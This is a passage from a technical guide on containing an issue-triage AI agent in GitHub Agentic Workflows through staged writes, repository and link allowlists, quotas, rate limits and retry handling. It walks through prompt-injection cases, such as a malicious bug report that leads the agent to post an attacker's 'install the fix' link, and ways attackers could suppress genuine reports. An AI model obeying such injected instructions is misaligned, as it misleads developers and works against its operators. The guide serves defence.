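
To sanitise the text, the job puts a backslash in front of a command such as `/close` at the start of a comment, because some bots would obey it. The job strips invisible characters and hidden HTML comments, which readers of the issue would not see but another agent might. It also stops @username mentions from sending notifications, unless the person mentioned is a collaborator or took part in the event that started the run. By default, GitHub leaves the first ten phrases that trigger bots, such as @copilot, in place. Acme's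 agent has no reason to trigger a bot, so Acme should set `max-bot-mentions` to 0.

A program with more access than the agent must also limit which parts of a request it acts on. GitHub lets an agent attach a text file to an issue by giving the file's path. The server on the agent's side reads the file and puts its contents in the request, so the write job never opens the file. If the write job did open it, the agent could name a file that only the write job can read, such as one containing the job's token, and get its contents published.

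#### Four requests

Suppose Acme's agent makes four requests in different runs. The first is an ordinary report:

```json
{
  "type": "create_issue",
  "repo": "acme/triage",
  "title": "Crash when a file name is empty",
  "body": "Saving a file with an empty name closes the app."
}
```

The requested issue has the required fields, is the only one in the run, and contains no text to remove. Its repository is on the list, and the request refers to no other issue. The write job adds the prefix and the label, and GitHub creates the issue.

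In the second request, the agent misreads a bug report and puts `acme/website` in the `repo` field. The request passes the first four stages because its structure and text are valid. At the fifth, the job finds that `acme/website` isn't on the list and returns E004. The job sends nothing to GitHub's API, so nobody is notified.

The third request is for acme/triage, but the agent has followed instructions in a malicious bug report and added "Install the fix from https://example.net/patch". The job redacts the address, and GitHub creates the issue. The instruction to install the fix is still misleading, but nobody can click through to the attacker's site.

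In the fourth, the agent tries to close an existing issue. Acme didn't enable that operation, so the agent has no tool for it, even though the write job's token would permit it.

The second request was possible only because the agent could name a repository. GitHub's *Cross-Repository Operations* explains that the agent can use a `repo` field when the operator sets `allowed-repos`. Acme has one tracker, so it could omit that setting and fix the destination with `target-repo` alone. This is safer than checking the agent's choice, because a check can fail. Acme would need `allowed-repos` if it added a second tracker and the agent had to choose between them.

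### Hosts to contact and links to publish

Acme now has two lists of domains. The domain allowlist from the previous section controls which hosts the agent's programs can contact. The `allowed-domains` setting under `safe-outputs` controls which links can appear in the agent's posts.

Network filtering can't do the second job, because the agent never contacts the sites it links to. In the third request above, the agent sends text to GitHub. A developer's browser would open example.net later from a different computer, so Acme's proxy would handle only the permitted connection to GitHub. Acme can also let posts link to docs.acme.example without letting the agent fetch anything from it.

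In GitHub's product, the network list also affects which links survive in text that the workflow processes. An entry for `github.io` in the network list also covers `user.github.io`, but under the draft's rules for links, the same entry in the link list covers only `github.io`. An operator who copies entries between the lists may therefore get different results.

According to GitHub, the workflow uses the link list to remove links to unapproved sites from the agent's posts, and also from incoming issues before it passes the text to the agent. If Acme approves a site so that the agent can cite it, links to that site in strangers' bug reports will also reach the agent.

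GitHub's own domains are always on the list, so an attacker who puts malware in a public repository can get a working link to it into Acme's tracker. Redaction also applies only to addresses that the program recognises as links. An instruction to search for a particular package contains no link, so the job leaves it unchanged. Link filtering makes phishing harder, but developers still have to treat instructions in an agent's issue with suspicion.

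### Which repository list applies

The draft allows two repository lists. A global one, `allowed-github-references`, covers every kind of write, and a type-specific one, `allowed-repos`, covers a single kind. If both exist, the type-specific list replaces the global one. For a request to write to repository *r*, let *S* be the type-specific list and *G* the global list. The draft permits a write to another repository if

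*r* ∈ *S*, or *S* doesn't exist and *r* ∈ *G*.

Suppose a security team at Acme sets the global list to acme/triage and assumes that no agent can write outside it. A developer then gives `create-issue` its own list, containing acme/website. Under the draft's rule, the agent may open issues in acme/website even though it isn't on the global list. To prevent this, the team would need a rule that requires a repository to be on both lists, which the draft doesn't have. An access token limited to acme/triage would still block the agent from opening issues in acme/website.

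The draft also contradicts itself about what happens when the operator configures no list. Its security section requires the system to reject writes to other repositories in that case. Its description of the global setting says the default is an empty list with "no cross-repository restrictions", and that the program should proceed when the list is empty. A programmer who followed the second passage would permit writes to all repositories, while an operator who relied on the first would expect writes to only one.

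The current reference and the code both support the strict reading. Without a `target-repo` setting, GitHub writes to the repository where the workflow runs. If the operator sets one, that repository is always allowed, and `allowed-repos` adds others to it. GitHub's *Add cross-repository allowlist validation (SEC-005)* (2026), a code change the project merged in February 2026, describes the shared function for checking repositories. The function accepts the default repository, checks any other against the list, and returns E004 if it finds no match.

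The same change shows that a rule in a specification protects only the parts of a program that apply it. An automated check had flagged seven files that handled a target repository without comparing it with an allowlist. Four didn't need to, including one that only built web addresses for display. The other three, which assigned work to an agent, started a new agent session, and saved an agent's notes to a repository, could act on a repository that nobody had approved. The file for creating issues was not among the seven, so this fault would not have affected Acme's agent, but an operator who used the other three would have depended on the token's scope for protection.

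The project added nine tests, three for each faulty file. Its automated check is cruder, because it looks for certain words in the code. A later report, GitHub's *Conformance Check Failure*, describes a false alarm the check raised about a file that mentioned a target repository. The check could also miss a fault, since a file can contain the right words but use them incorrectly.

Operators who read the draft alongside the current reference will find other differences:

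| Question | Draft 1.29.8 | Current reference |
|---|---|---|
| What does `allowed-github-references` do? | Limits where the agent can write | Controls whether mentions of other repositories become working references |
| Can repository lists use wildcards? | No | Yes, for example `acme/*` |
| What happens without a list of link domains? | No filtering by domain | Removes links outside GitHub's domains |
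| What replaces an unapproved link? | A notice that the domain is unauthorised | "(redacted)" |

The difference in the first row is the most dangerous. Under the current reference, an operator who follows the draft and uses `allowed-github-references` to restrict writes would only change how text appears. Acme should put its limit in `target-repo` and `allowed-repos` instead. The configuration above lists acme/triage under both because the draft requires the target to be on the type-specific list and the current reference accepts it there.

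Operators can also misread two similar settings. `target-repo: "*"` lets the agent pick any repository, so only the token limits where it writes. A second `allowed-repos` setting, under `tools.github`, controls which repositories the agent can read through its GitHub tools. If the operator omits that list, the agent can read every repository the token can reach. Acme needs acme/app and acme/billing on the read list but not on the write list.

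One small package in the Go programming language, *repoallowlist*, treats a missing list differently again. Its documentation specifies that an empty list allows every repository (pkg.go.dev, 2026). An operator can check any product by asking the agent to write to an unlisted test repository and confirming that the request fails.

### Previewing and approving writes

GitHub offers a preview called staged mode, in which the write job makes no changes and instead prints in the run summary what it would have posted. The name is confusing because the product stages every write, with or without this mode. An operator can preview one kind of write while the others run normally.

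Acme could run its agent in staged mode for two weeks and compare the previews with what its maintainers would have filed. This would reveal a wrong label, a broken link rule or repeated reports of the same bug, but not how the agent responds to an attack that nobody tried during those weeks. Acme's workflow runs in acme/app. If that repository is public, its readers can see the workflow's logs, so a preview that contains a payment key could expose it.

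Staged mode also doesn't wait for approval. Once Acme turns it off, the agent's next issue appears without review. If Acme wants a person to approve real writes, it can keep the write credentials in a GitHub environment, a protected group of settings that can require a reviewer before a job starts. The reviewer then approves all of a run's requests at once, which is faster than approving each one. GitHub also applies the environment to some jobs that run before and after the agent, so Acme should check where the run stops and what the reviewer can see at that point.

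### The costs of checking later

An agent that writes directly to GitHub gets an issue number or an error within seconds. With staged writes, it gets only a confirmation that the server recorded the request. In the draft, the server replies "success" even if the write job later rejects the request with E004. Acme's agent might therefore finish its run and report that it filed an issue that doesn't exist. It also can't correct the repository name and try again.

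GitHub reduces this problem by running some checks earlier. The server immediately reports structural errors and rejects comments whose whole text is a placeholder such as "test". For writes that depend on each other, the server gives each request an identifier. The agent can use these identifiers to specify, for example, that a comment should appear only if an earlier update succeeds. If the update fails, the job skips the comment but doesn't undo anything that already succeeded.

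The delay also has benefits. The write job receives all of a run's requests before it sends any, so it can apply the count limit to the whole set, and GitHub can scan the set for threats first. The delay also gives a hijacked agent less information. If every refusal came back immediately, the agent could try one repository after another until one worked. A delay of a few minutes matters little for an overnight triage agent. It would matter more for an agent that answers a customer in a live conversation, where an operator might prefer a gateway that holds the credentials, checks each request and carries it out immediately.

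#### Blocked work

Strict rules also block useful writes. A customer might link to a test file on a file-sharing site, and the developers would see only "(redacted)". By default, GitHub rejects a request to add a label that doesn't exist in the repository, so renaming a label can break a workflow that uses the old name. Repository matching is case-sensitive, so `acme/triage` in a list doesn't match `Acme/triage`.

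These failures are easier to repair than an unwanted post. An administrator or maintainer can correct the configuration and rerun the saved requests from GitHub's maintenance workflow. But someone has to notice the failures first, and Acme turned off the automatic failure issues. It should send E004 and other refusals to a private channel, which would also help it spot attacks. Twenty refusals for the same unknown repository suggest that someone is trying to redirect the agent, though a single refusal may be a typing error.

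#### Lists that grow

Allowlists tend to grow because people add an entry when something breaks but have no similar prompt to remove old ones. If Acme starts with one repository, adds one a month and removes none, it has 37 after three years, almost as many as the 40 that its broad token covered. Acme would also have to extend the token each time, so the token would become a weaker backstop as the list grew.

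The draft requires the error message for a refused repository to include the configuration that would permit it. This helps someone who made a mistake, but a busy maintainer may paste it in without asking why the agent wanted to write there.

A wildcard such as `acme/*` saves maintenance by approving repositories in advance, but it covers every repository Acme owns now or creates later, including public ones. Acme rarely needs a new tracker, so it should accept the extra work of listing repositories by name.

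Labels are harder to restrict because a large project may have hundreds. GitHub considers a complete allowlist impractical in such repositories, so it offers patterns for blocking labels instead. For example, an operator can block every label that starts with `~` and allow the rest. But with a blocklist, the agent can use a new label that triggers a deployment until someone blocks it. If labels trigger other automation, a short allowlist of the five or ten labels the agent uses is safer.

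Acme can base its pruning on what the agent has done. GitHub puts a hidden marker with the workflow's name in the issues, comments and pull requests that a workflow creates, and anyone with access can search for it:

`org:acme "gh-aw-workflow-id: triage" in:body`

If a repository on the list received no issues from the agent in the past three months, Acme can remove it from both the list and the token. Custom jobs that call GitHub's API directly don't add the marker automatically, so Acme would have to add it to those jobs before relying on the search.

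Edit access to the lists also needs to be controlled, because anyone who can change the repository file that contains them can approve a new target. GitHub computes a hash (a short fingerprint) of the configuration when it compiles the workflow and checks it before the run. This catches changes made between those two steps, but not a change that someone commits and compiles in the normal way. The draft recommends code review and branch protection, a setting that blocks direct changes to important branches. An agent that can push code needs particular care, because it could propose an edit to its own allowlist, and a reviewer might miss one added line among many.

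## Limiting how many writes run at once and in total

The allowlists leave Acme's agent with one kind of write in one repository, but it could still file thousands of issues there. Operators can set three different limits on an agent's calls, and people often confuse them:

- A concurrency cap is the largest number of calls that may be in progress at the same moment.
- A rate limit is the largest number of calls allowed in a period of time.
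- A write quota is the largest total number of writes allowed in one run or in another stated scope.

Suppose Acme sets a limit of five and its agent, stuck in a loop, tries to file a sixth issue. A concurrency cap of five lets the sixth issue go out as soon as one of the first five calls finishes. A rate limit of five a minute delays it by at most a minute. A quota of five per run blocks it for the rest of the run.

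### How a program enforces each limit

Programs usually enforce a concurrency cap with a semaphore, which is a counter of free slots. In pseudocode:

```text
free = 5

function write(request):
    wait until free > 0, then set free = free - 1
    try:
        return send(request)
    finally:
        free = free + 1
```

Each call takes a slot before it starts, or waits if none is free. The `finally` block returns the slot when the call ends, even if the call fails. Without `finally`, five failed calls would use up every slot, and the agent could no longer write.

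The count can still be wrong if the program stops waiting for a slow call. The program frees the slot, but GitHub may still be processing the request when the next call starts, so six requests can be in progress under a cap of five.

A common way to enforce a rate limit is a token bucket. (These tokens are only a count and have nothing to do with access tokens.) The bucket starts full, each write removes one token, and the program adds tokens at a steady rate until the bucket is full again:

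```text
tokens = burst
last = now()

function may_write():
    t = now()
    tokens = min(burst, tokens + rate * (t - last))
    last = t
    if tokens < 1:
        return false
    tokens = tokens - 1
    return true
```

With a burst of five and a rate of one token a minute, an agent that has filed nothing for a while can file five issues immediately and then one a minute. The burst is useful because a run may find several bugs at once, but it also lets the agent file six issues in a single minute, five from the full bucket and one from the refill. An operator who wants at most *N* writes in any minute therefore has to keep the burst plus one minute's refill at or below *N*.

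Some programs instead count the writes in each clock minute and reset the count when the next minute begins. This is simpler, but a limit of five writes a minute allows five at 12:00:59 and five more a second later.

A quota needs only a counter that never goes down:

```text
used = 0

function may_write():
    if used >= quota:
        return false
    used = used + 1
    return true
```

Checking the quota and adding to `used` must happen as one step. Suppose the quota is five, the agent has filed four issues, and five more calls arrive together. If all five read `used` before any of them changes it, they all read four and proceed, and the agent ends up filing nine issues. Semaphores and token buckets can have the same problem. The semaphores built into programming languages usually handle it correctly, but a counter kept in a shared file may not.

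### How many writes each limit allows

Let *L* be the time one call takes and *T* the time between the start of a fault and the moment someone stops the agent. Under a concurrency cap of *c*, each slot completes one call every *L* seconds, so the number of completed writes is about

*c* × *T* / *L*.

If each call creates one issue and takes half a second, and someone notices the problem after ten minutes, a cap of five concurrent calls allows 5 × 600 / 0.5 = 6,000 issues. Closing them at five minutes each would take 500 hours. Even a cap of one, the strictest possible, allows 1,200 issues.

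Acme also doesn't control *L*. If GitHub started answering in a tenth of a second, a cap of one would allow 6,000 issues in the same ten minutes.

A token bucket with burst *b* and rate *r* allows at most *b* + *rT* writes, because the agent can use the full bucket and then every token that arrives during *T*. A quota of *Q* allows at most *Q* writes regardless of *T* or *L*, so the bound holds even if nobody ever notices the fault.

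The table applies these formulas to a call time of half a second:

| Limit | Writes in 10 minutes | Writes in 8 hours |
|---|---|---|
| Concurrency cap of 5 | 6,000 | 288,000 |
| Concurrency cap of 1 | 1,200 | 57,600 |
| Token bucket, burst of 5, one token a minute | 15 | 485 |
| Quota of 5 | 5 | 5 |

A concurrency cap slows the damage an agent can do but doesn't limit the total. It also limits how many requests are in flight when someone stops the agent. GitHub may carry out those requests even after the agent's process has ended, so stopping an agent with a cap of five can leave five more issues to clean up, compared with a hundred for an agent making a hundred parallel calls.

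If Acme uses all three limits, the smallest bound applies, which is the quota of five. The cap and the bucket then affect only the timing. Timing can still help, because if the agent can file only one issue every ten minutes, a maintainer who sees a strange first issue has ten minutes to prevent the second, instead of having to clean up five that appeared within a second.

### Where to put the limit

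A model can request several tool calls in one response, and the program that runs the tools may carry them out in parallel. Developers can turn this off with the `parallel_tool_calls` setting in OpenAI's API or `disable_parallel_tool_use` in Anthropic's. The model then requests at most one call per response and receives the result before it requests another.

This works like a concurrency cap of one for a single conversation. The model also takes time to produce each call. If producing a call takes three seconds and running it takes half a second, a looping agent files about 170 issues in ten minutes, compared with 1,200 for a script that sends them back to back.

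The setting doesn't limit the total number of writes, and it counts tool calls, each of which can make more than one write. A single call could use a tool that accepts a list of issues, or run a shell script that posts a thousand issues if the script can find a credential. Two agents running at the same time can also each make a call.

The program that runs the tools is a better place for a quota because it handles every tool call its agent makes. With a quota of five, it can refuse the sixth `create_issue` call whether the model requested the calls together or one by one. But if the program keeps the count in memory, a restart resets it to zero, so an agent that crashes and restarts after every fourth issue would never reach the quota. Separate copies of the program would also keep separate counts.

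A gateway shared by all agents can count writes across agent restarts and copies. If it also holds the only write credential, an agent can't avoid the count by contacting GitHub directly. If the gateway itself runs in several copies, it should refuse writes when the storage for their shared count is unavailable, because otherwise an outage would remove the limit. Refusing writes also stops legitimate work during the outage.

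Acme could turn off parallel calls and keep a quota in the gateway. If a software update removed the parallel-call setting, the agent might file issues faster, but the quota would still limit the total.

### GitHub's own limits

Services limit their users too, so an operator might hope that GitHub would stop a runaway agent. GitHub's *Rate limits for the REST API* lists several limits that apply at the same time. If each call takes half a second, they allow the following:

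| GitHub's limit | New issues it would allow in one minute |
|---|---|
| 100 requests in progress at once | 12,000 |
| 900 points a minute, at 5 points for most writes | 180 |
| 90 seconds of CPU time a minute | About 180, if CPU time equals response time |
| In general, 80 content-creating requests a minute | 80 |
| In general, 500 content-creating requests an hour | 80, until the hour's total reaches 500 |

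The limit on content-creating requests takes effect first. A loop with five parallel calls tries to file ten issues a second, so it reaches the limit of 80 a minute after eight seconds. If it uses all of each minute's allowance, it reaches the limit of 500 just after the sixth minute. It files about 500 issues in ten minutes. With only a concurrency cap of five, it would file 6,000. The limit of 100 parallel requests would take effect before the limit of 80 a minute only if each call took more than 75 seconds.

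The loop in the earlier example, which files an issue every two seconds for eight hours, never exceeds the limit of 80 a minute. It reaches the hourly limit of 500 after about 17 minutes and has to wait before filing more. Over the night it files roughly 4,000 issues instead of 14,400, and cleaning them up still takes more than 330 hours.

GitHub also limits the total number of requests an hour, including reads. For `GITHUB_TOKEN`, the token built into GitHub Actions, the limit is usually 1,000 an hour for each repository. If an agent reads the tracker once before it files each issue, 1,000 requests cover 500 issues, which is also the hourly limit on new content. If it needs three requests per issue, it reaches the request limit first, after 333 issues. A GitHub App gets at least 5,000 requests an hour, so it would have to make more than ten requests per issue to reach the request limit first.

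These limits are a weak safety control, mainly because GitHub set them for a different purpose. GitHub says they are meant to ensure consistent access, prevent abuse and denial-of-service attacks, and keep the system available. Five hundred junk issues an hour would overwhelm the people who read acme/triage without threatening GitHub's servers.

An operator can't plan around the limits either. GitHub may change the secondary limits, which include all those in the table, without notice. It may also apply limits for undisclosed reasons, and it offers no way to check how close an account is to a secondary limit.

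When an agent reaches a limit, GitHub refuses its requests for a while and then accepts them again. A correctly written program waits and then continues, so the limit only delays the junk issues. GitHub may ban an integration that keeps sending requests while over the limit. A ban would stop Acme's agent, including its useful work, but Acme couldn't predict when.

A program can also follow all of GitHub's advice and still flood an issue tracker. GitHub's *Best practices for using the REST API* recommends sending requests one at a time and waiting at least a second between writes. If each call takes half a second, a program that does this can file 40 issues a minute, which is under the limit of 80, and 500 issues in twelve and a half minutes.

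If the agent uses a maintainer's personal access token, its requests count towards that person's hourly limit of 5,000. A runaway agent could use up the requests that the maintainer's own scripts need to close the junk issues. This is another reason to give the agent its own GitHub App.

### What a quota counts

In GitHub Agentic Workflows, the `max` setting is a quota for one kind of write in one run. The write job applies it to the complete list of requests, so parallel calls by the agent can't cause the counting error described above.

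GitHub's default quotas vary with the kind of write:

| Kind of write | Default quota per run |
|---|---|
| Create an issue | 1 |
| Post a comment | 1 |
| Add labels | 5 calls |
| Close a pull request | 10 |
| Report a code scanning alert | Unlimited |

The write job counts each kind of write separately, and nothing limits the total. If Acme kept its limit of five issues and also allowed three comments and the default five calls to add labels, one run could make 13 writes. By default, each label call can add up to ten labels, so those five calls could add 50.

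A single request can also change more than one thing. If an operator turns on `close-older-issues`, the write job can close up to ten earlier issues from the same workflow each time it creates a new one. With another setting, `group-by-day`, the job posts new content as a comment on an issue from the same day, which doesn't count toward `max`. Acme should leave both settings off if it wants five requests to make at most five visible changes.

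Operators should explicitly set every quota they depend on, because the documentation is inconsistent. The current reference gives a default of three for starting other workflows, but GitHub's *Rate Limiting Controls* gives one. The draft specification also calls `max: 0` invalid in one passage and says in another that it turns off that kind of write.

An operator who runs a gateway could replace the separate quotas with a single budget in points. GitHub's API limit works this way. Most reads use one point and most writes use five, but those values reflect the load on GitHub. Acme could set point values that reflect harm, such as one for a label and five for a public issue. A budget of 30 points would allow five issues and five labels, or six issues alone. Acme would have to guess the point values, but even a rough guess would limit the total across all kinds of write.

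#### Rejecting the whole batch

If Acme's agent asks to create six issues in a run with a quota of five, the write job rejects all six with error E002 before it contacts GitHub's API. According to GitHub's draft, this is because partial execution may leave things in an inconsistent state. For example, if an agent splits a plan into six linked tasks, publishing only five would make the plan look complete when it isn't.

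The rule also makes sense for safety, because a run that exceeds its quota may have gone wrong, and the job can't determine which of the six requests are sound. If it published the first five, an agent stuck in a loop might leave five copies of the same report in the tracker.

But the rule gives an attacker a way to suppress real reports. Suppose the agent has found three genuine bugs, and a malicious bug report persuades it to file three more issues. The total of six exceeds the limit, so the genuine reports don't appear either. An attacker who wants to delay news of a security hole might find this more useful than spam.

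Acme can limit the harm by sending E002 errors to its private channel, as it does with refused repositories. A maintainer can then look at the rejected requests, whose titles are listed in the error message. The message also shows how to raise the limit. A maintainer who raises it and reruns the batch without reading the titles would publish the attacker's issues along with the genuine ones.

### Runs that don't share a quota

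Each run of a workflow gets its own quota. For simplicity, the draft requires no coordination between concurrent runs, so *R* runs with a quota of *Q* each can make *R* × *Q* writes.

If Acme starts a run for every new bug report, strangers control *R*. Someone who files 40 reports in acme/app starts 40 runs, and those runs can file 200 issues in acme/triage. No run exceeds its quota, so the write jobs report no errors. If Acme instead runs the agent once a night over all the new reports, *R* is one, and the quota limits the agent to five issues a night. However, a report of a serious crash may then wait until morning.

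GitHub's `user-rate-limit` setting cancels a workflow run if the same user has started too many recently. An operator can allow between one and ten runs per user in a window of up to three hours. With five runs an hour and five issues per run, one account could make the workflow open 25 issues an hour, but an attacker with ten accounts could make it open 250. By default, the setting exempts anyone with write access to the repository, so it doesn't stop a faulty script that runs under a maintainer's account.

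#### Running one at a time

According to GitHub's *Concurrency Control*, workflow runs for different issues can proceed at the same time. By default, only one agent job runs at a time for each AI engine, but the jobs that carry out the writes can overlap. An operator can make the write jobs take turns:

```yaml
safe-outputs:
  concurrency-group: "safe-outputs-${{ github.repository }}"
```

Making runs take turns helps when two runs would otherwise file the same bug at the same moment. It is a concurrency cap of one applied to runs, so it limits only the speed of filing and doesn't reduce the total. Forty runs in sequence can still file 200 issues. If each of Acme's runs took four minutes, an eight-hour night would have room for 120 runs in sequence, which could file 600 issues.

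Running jobs one at a time can also lose work. GitHub's *Using concurrency* explains that with `cancel-in-progress: true`, a new run cancels any run in progress in the same group. The setting above uses `false`, so a write job that has started can finish. But GitHub warns that if someone starts many runs at once and their jobs share a group, GitHub cancels all but the latest. The `job-discriminator` setting avoids this by giving each run its own group, but the runs can then overlap again. Acme should start several test runs together and check that all their issues appear.

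#### Sharing one counter

To limit the total across runs, every run has to draw on the same count. Acme could keep a daily budget in a database and have its gateway run this command before each write:

```sql
UPDATE write_budget
SET used = used + 1
WHERE scope = 'acme/triage'
  AND day = CURRENT_DATE
  AND used < 20;
```

The gateway sends the write if the command changes a row and refuses it otherwise. The database checks the number and increases it in one step, so two runs can't both take the last place. If nobody has created a row for the day, the command changes nothing, so the mistake blocks writes instead of allowing them.

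With this budget, the 40 runs can file at most 20 issues between them. But one bad run can use up the budget for all the others. Acme should therefore also keep the quota of five issues per run, so that an attacker needs at least four runs to exhaust the day's budget.

An operator who wants to keep GitHub's write job could try to build a shared limit from the `max` setting, which accepts a value supplied when a run starts. A program could look up how much of the daily budget remains and pass that number to each new run. If five writes remain, two runs that start together might each be allowed all five, so the program has to reserve the writes before it starts a run.

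In the draft, `max: -1` means unlimited. If the agent has used 21 writes from a budget of 20, setting `max` to the remaining budget gives −1 and removes the limit. The program should start a run only if the remaining budget is at least one.

#### Counting by credential

A gateway can also attach the quota to the credential used for the writes. If Acme gives the triage agent its own GitHub App and allows that App 20 writes a day, the limit covers every run, every copy of the agent and every workflow that uses the App. If a developer later adds a second workflow, its writes count toward the same limit without extra setup, provided it uses the same App and writes through the gateway.

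The gateway has to count writes by App, not by access token. GitHub Apps use short-lived tokens, so if each run received a new token, counting by token would reset the count to zero every run. An agent with access to two Apps would have two quotas. If an unrelated program uses the triage agent's App, they share the same 20 writes, so a busy day for one can block the other.

The table compares the remedies for 40 runs that each try to file five issues in one night:

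| Control | Issues filed | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Quota of 5 per run | 200 | Whoever starts the runs controls the total |
| The same quota, with runs taking turns | 200, more slowly | GitHub may cancel waiting runs |
| Shared counter of 20 a day | 20 | Writes stop if the counter is unavailable |
| Quota of 20 a day per GitHub App | 20 | Programs that share the App compete for writes |

The most practical choice for Acme is one run a night with a quota of five, because this needs no extra storage. If Acme later decides to start a run for each bug report, it should first add a daily quota for the App.

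### Choosing the numbers

A quota that is too low blocks real work, and rejecting whole batches blocks more of it. Suppose Acme previews its agent for two weeks and finds that it usually requests two or three issues a night and never more than seven. With a quota of five, a night with seven real bugs would produce no issues. A quota of eight would have allowed every genuine request from those two weeks, but the worst fault would take 40 minutes to clean up instead of 25. Acme can reasonably keep the lower quota if someone checks for rejected batches each morning; otherwise, eight is the better choice.

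Acme gains very little from parallel writes because the job runs overnight. Writing five issues at half a second each takes 2.5 seconds one at a time, or 6.5 seconds with a one-second pause between them.

Parallel reads can save more time than parallel writes, because the agent may look through hundreds of old reports before it files a new one. Acme can set separate caps, such as ten reads at once but only one write. The domain allowlist must also cover reads, because the URL of a read request can carry data out.

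Large jobs need a higher quota, but they may not need more parallel writes. If Acme wanted to copy 2,000 issues into a new tracker, GitHub's limit of 500 content-creating requests an hour would make the job take at least three hours. Twenty parallel workers would finish only a few minutes sooner than one worker that pauses between writes, and they would leave up to 20 requests in flight if someone had to stop the job. Acme can raise the quota to 2,000 for that run and leave the nightly quota unchanged. This is safer than setting `max: -1` because the quota would still stop the script if a bug made it start again from the first issue after reaching the last.

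## Retries, duplicate posts and stopping a faulty run

Suppose Acme's gateway sends GitHub a request to create an issue and the request times out. The request may never have arrived, or the network may have dropped the reply after GitHub created the issue. The timeout looks the same in both cases, so retrying may create a duplicate issue, but not retrying may leave a bug unreported.

*Ensuring idempotency*, from Amazon's cloud business AWS, says that a timeout or server error can occur after the change has already happened. GitHub's *Troubleshooting the REST API* says that GitHub terminates a request that takes more than ten seconds and returns a "Server Error" message. That message doesn't show whether GitHub stored the issue first. A gateway can cause the same problem by timing out too early. If it stops waiting after five seconds and GitHub finishes after seven, the issue exists but the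 gateway never receives its number. Acme should set the gateway to wait longer than ten seconds.

### Which writes are safe to repeat

An idempotent operation has the same effect whether a program carries it out once or several times. Adding the label `needs-review` to an issue is idempotent because adding it again changes nothing, but creating an issue is not, because each successful attempt makes a new one. GitHub's draft specification for staged writes lists adding a label, removing a label and hiding a comment as idempotent, and creating an issue, a discussion or a comment as non-idempotent.

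Some services reject certain duplicate writes. GitHub requires label names to be unique within a repository, so a second attempt to create the same label gets an `already_exists` error. But it accepts any number of issues with the same title.

A late retry can cause trouble even when the write is idempotent. If an agent adds the `needs-review` label, a maintainer removes it, and a retry arrives a minute later, the label comes back.

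### How duplicates add up

Suppose every attempt succeeds on GitHub's side, each reply goes missing independently with probability *p*, and the gateway makes up to *r* retries. The first attempt always creates an issue. The second happens only if the first reply goes missing, the third only if the first two do, and so on. The average number of issues per request is therefore

1 + *p* + *p*² + … + *p*^*r* = (1 − *p*^(*r*+1)) / (1 − *p*).

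If each reply has a probability *p* = 0.1 of going missing and the agent makes up to *r* = 3 retries, each request creates 1.11 issues on average, so 50 requests produce about 56. If every reply goes missing, each request creates *r* + 1 = 4 issues, so 50 requests produce 200. Closing the 150 extra copies at five minutes each takes 12.5 hours.

Lost replies tend to come together, so the worst case is more likely than the formula suggests. GitHub's *Incident with API Requests* (2026) describes nine minutes in March 2026 when server errors on the REST API peaked at about 5%, with sustained timeouts on some endpoints. The 5% isn't an estimate of *p*, since some of those requests may have changed nothing, but a program using one of those endpoints could have lost several replies in a row. In 2017 a user of the issue tracker Jira reported a similar failure in the forum thread *Duplicate Jira issues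 created*. The back end slowed down while a script was creating a batch of issues, and the user got about eight duplicates of each one.

A quota misses these duplicates if it counts requests but not retries. With a quota of five requests and three retries each, Acme's agent could create 20 issues. The gateway should count each attempt before sending it, which would limit the agent to five issues. But if attempts keep failing, the agent may use up its quota on retries for one bug.

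Retries also multiply when several programs make them. If the gateway tries each request four times, and the web library underneath it makes four attempts for each of those, one request can create 16 issues. Settings also differ in whether they count the first attempt. One AWS software kit includes it in `max_attempts`, so a value of 1 turns retries off. Elsewhere, a setting of three "retries" may allow four attempts.

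The model can also retry. If a tool call returns "timeout", the model may try to create the issue again under a slightly different title. Staged writes make this less likely because the agent gets confirmation as soon as the server records the request.

AWS's *REL04-BP04 Make mutating operations idempotent* explains that a program can easily act at most once, by never retrying, or at least once, by retrying until it gets a confirmation, but that acting exactly once is harder. For a POST to a service that can't detect repeated requests, AWS recommends the at-most-once setting in its tool for long-running programs, with retries disabled. Acting at most once also suits Acme, because a missing report can wait until the next night's run.

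### Two workers and one bug

Duplicates can appear even when every reply arrives. Suppose two people report the same crash in acme/app and two runs handle the reports at the same time:

| Time | Run A | Run B |
|---|---|---|
| 02:00:00 | Searches acme/triage and finds nothing | |
| 02:00:01 | | Searches acme/triage and finds nothing |
| 02:00:02 | Creates an issue | |
| 02:00:03 | | Creates a second issue |

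Programmers call this a check-then-create race. Both runs followed the rule "search before you file", but B's search result was out of date by the time B acted on it.

A slow search index can cause the same failure with only one worker. In *How do I ensure issue creation is idempotent?*, a thread on Atlassian's developer forum, a user describes storing a unique identifier in each Jira issue and searching for it before creating another. Jira's newer search endpoint doesn't guarantee that a newly created issue appears in the results. One participant tested it and saw changes appear immediately or very quickly, but another had recently found a duplicate after a search missed an issue created about five seconds earlier. A few successful tests therefore don't show that searching first is safe.

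#### A single writer

If only one job writes at a time, the second can search after the first has finished. GitHub's concurrency groups make write jobs take turns, but by default only one job can wait. If 40 write jobs start together, one runs, one waits, and GitHub cancels the other 38. In May, GitHub (2026) introduced the setting `queue: max`, which lets up to 100 wait. Acme should check that its compiled workflow uses this setting before it relies on the queue.

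The search for an existing issue has to happen during the write job's turn. Otherwise, two agents can both decide to file the same crash before either write job begins, and the jobs then file it twice even though they run one at a time. The `deduplicate-by-title` setting helps because the write job itself compares the new title with those of open and recently closed issues. GitHub lets operators require an exact match or allow a set number of single-character edits. Acme should require an exact match, since "Payment fails with error 401" and "Payment fails with error 402" differ by one character and may be different bugs. An exact match won't catch a duplicate that the model has reworded.

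Title matching also lets strangers suppress a report if they can open issues in acme/triage. They could file an empty issue under the title they expect the agent to use, and the write job would drop the agent's issue as a duplicate. With `deduplicate-by-labels`, Acme can also require the existing issue to have a label, which a stranger normally can't add. The label should be permanent, such as `agent-filed`. If Acme used `needs-review`, the check would stop working once a maintainer reviewed the issue and removed the label.

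#### A lock for each item

With a single writer, reports of unrelated bugs have to wait for one another. A narrower lock covers one item, so only workers handling that item take turns. By default, GitHub puts the issue number in the name of the concurrency group, so two runs of a workflow for report 101 can't overlap, but runs for reports 101 and 102 can. If both reports describe the same crash, the two runs can still post duplicates. To prevent this, Acme would need a lock named after the crash, and both runs would have to use the same name.

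#### A unique marker

The gateway can add a line such as `acme-key: app-101` to each issue. After a timeout, it searches for that line to find out whether the issue exists. The marker doesn't prevent race conditions. A slow search index can also hide the marker, but an overnight agent can wait ten minutes before it searches. The gateway should accept a match only if Acme's own GitHub App posted it, because anyone can copy a marker from a public tracker.

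GitHub's built-in marker isn't enough here because it identifies the workflow, not the individual request. The model can't add a hidden marker because the write job strips HTML comments from the model's text.

#### Idempotency keys

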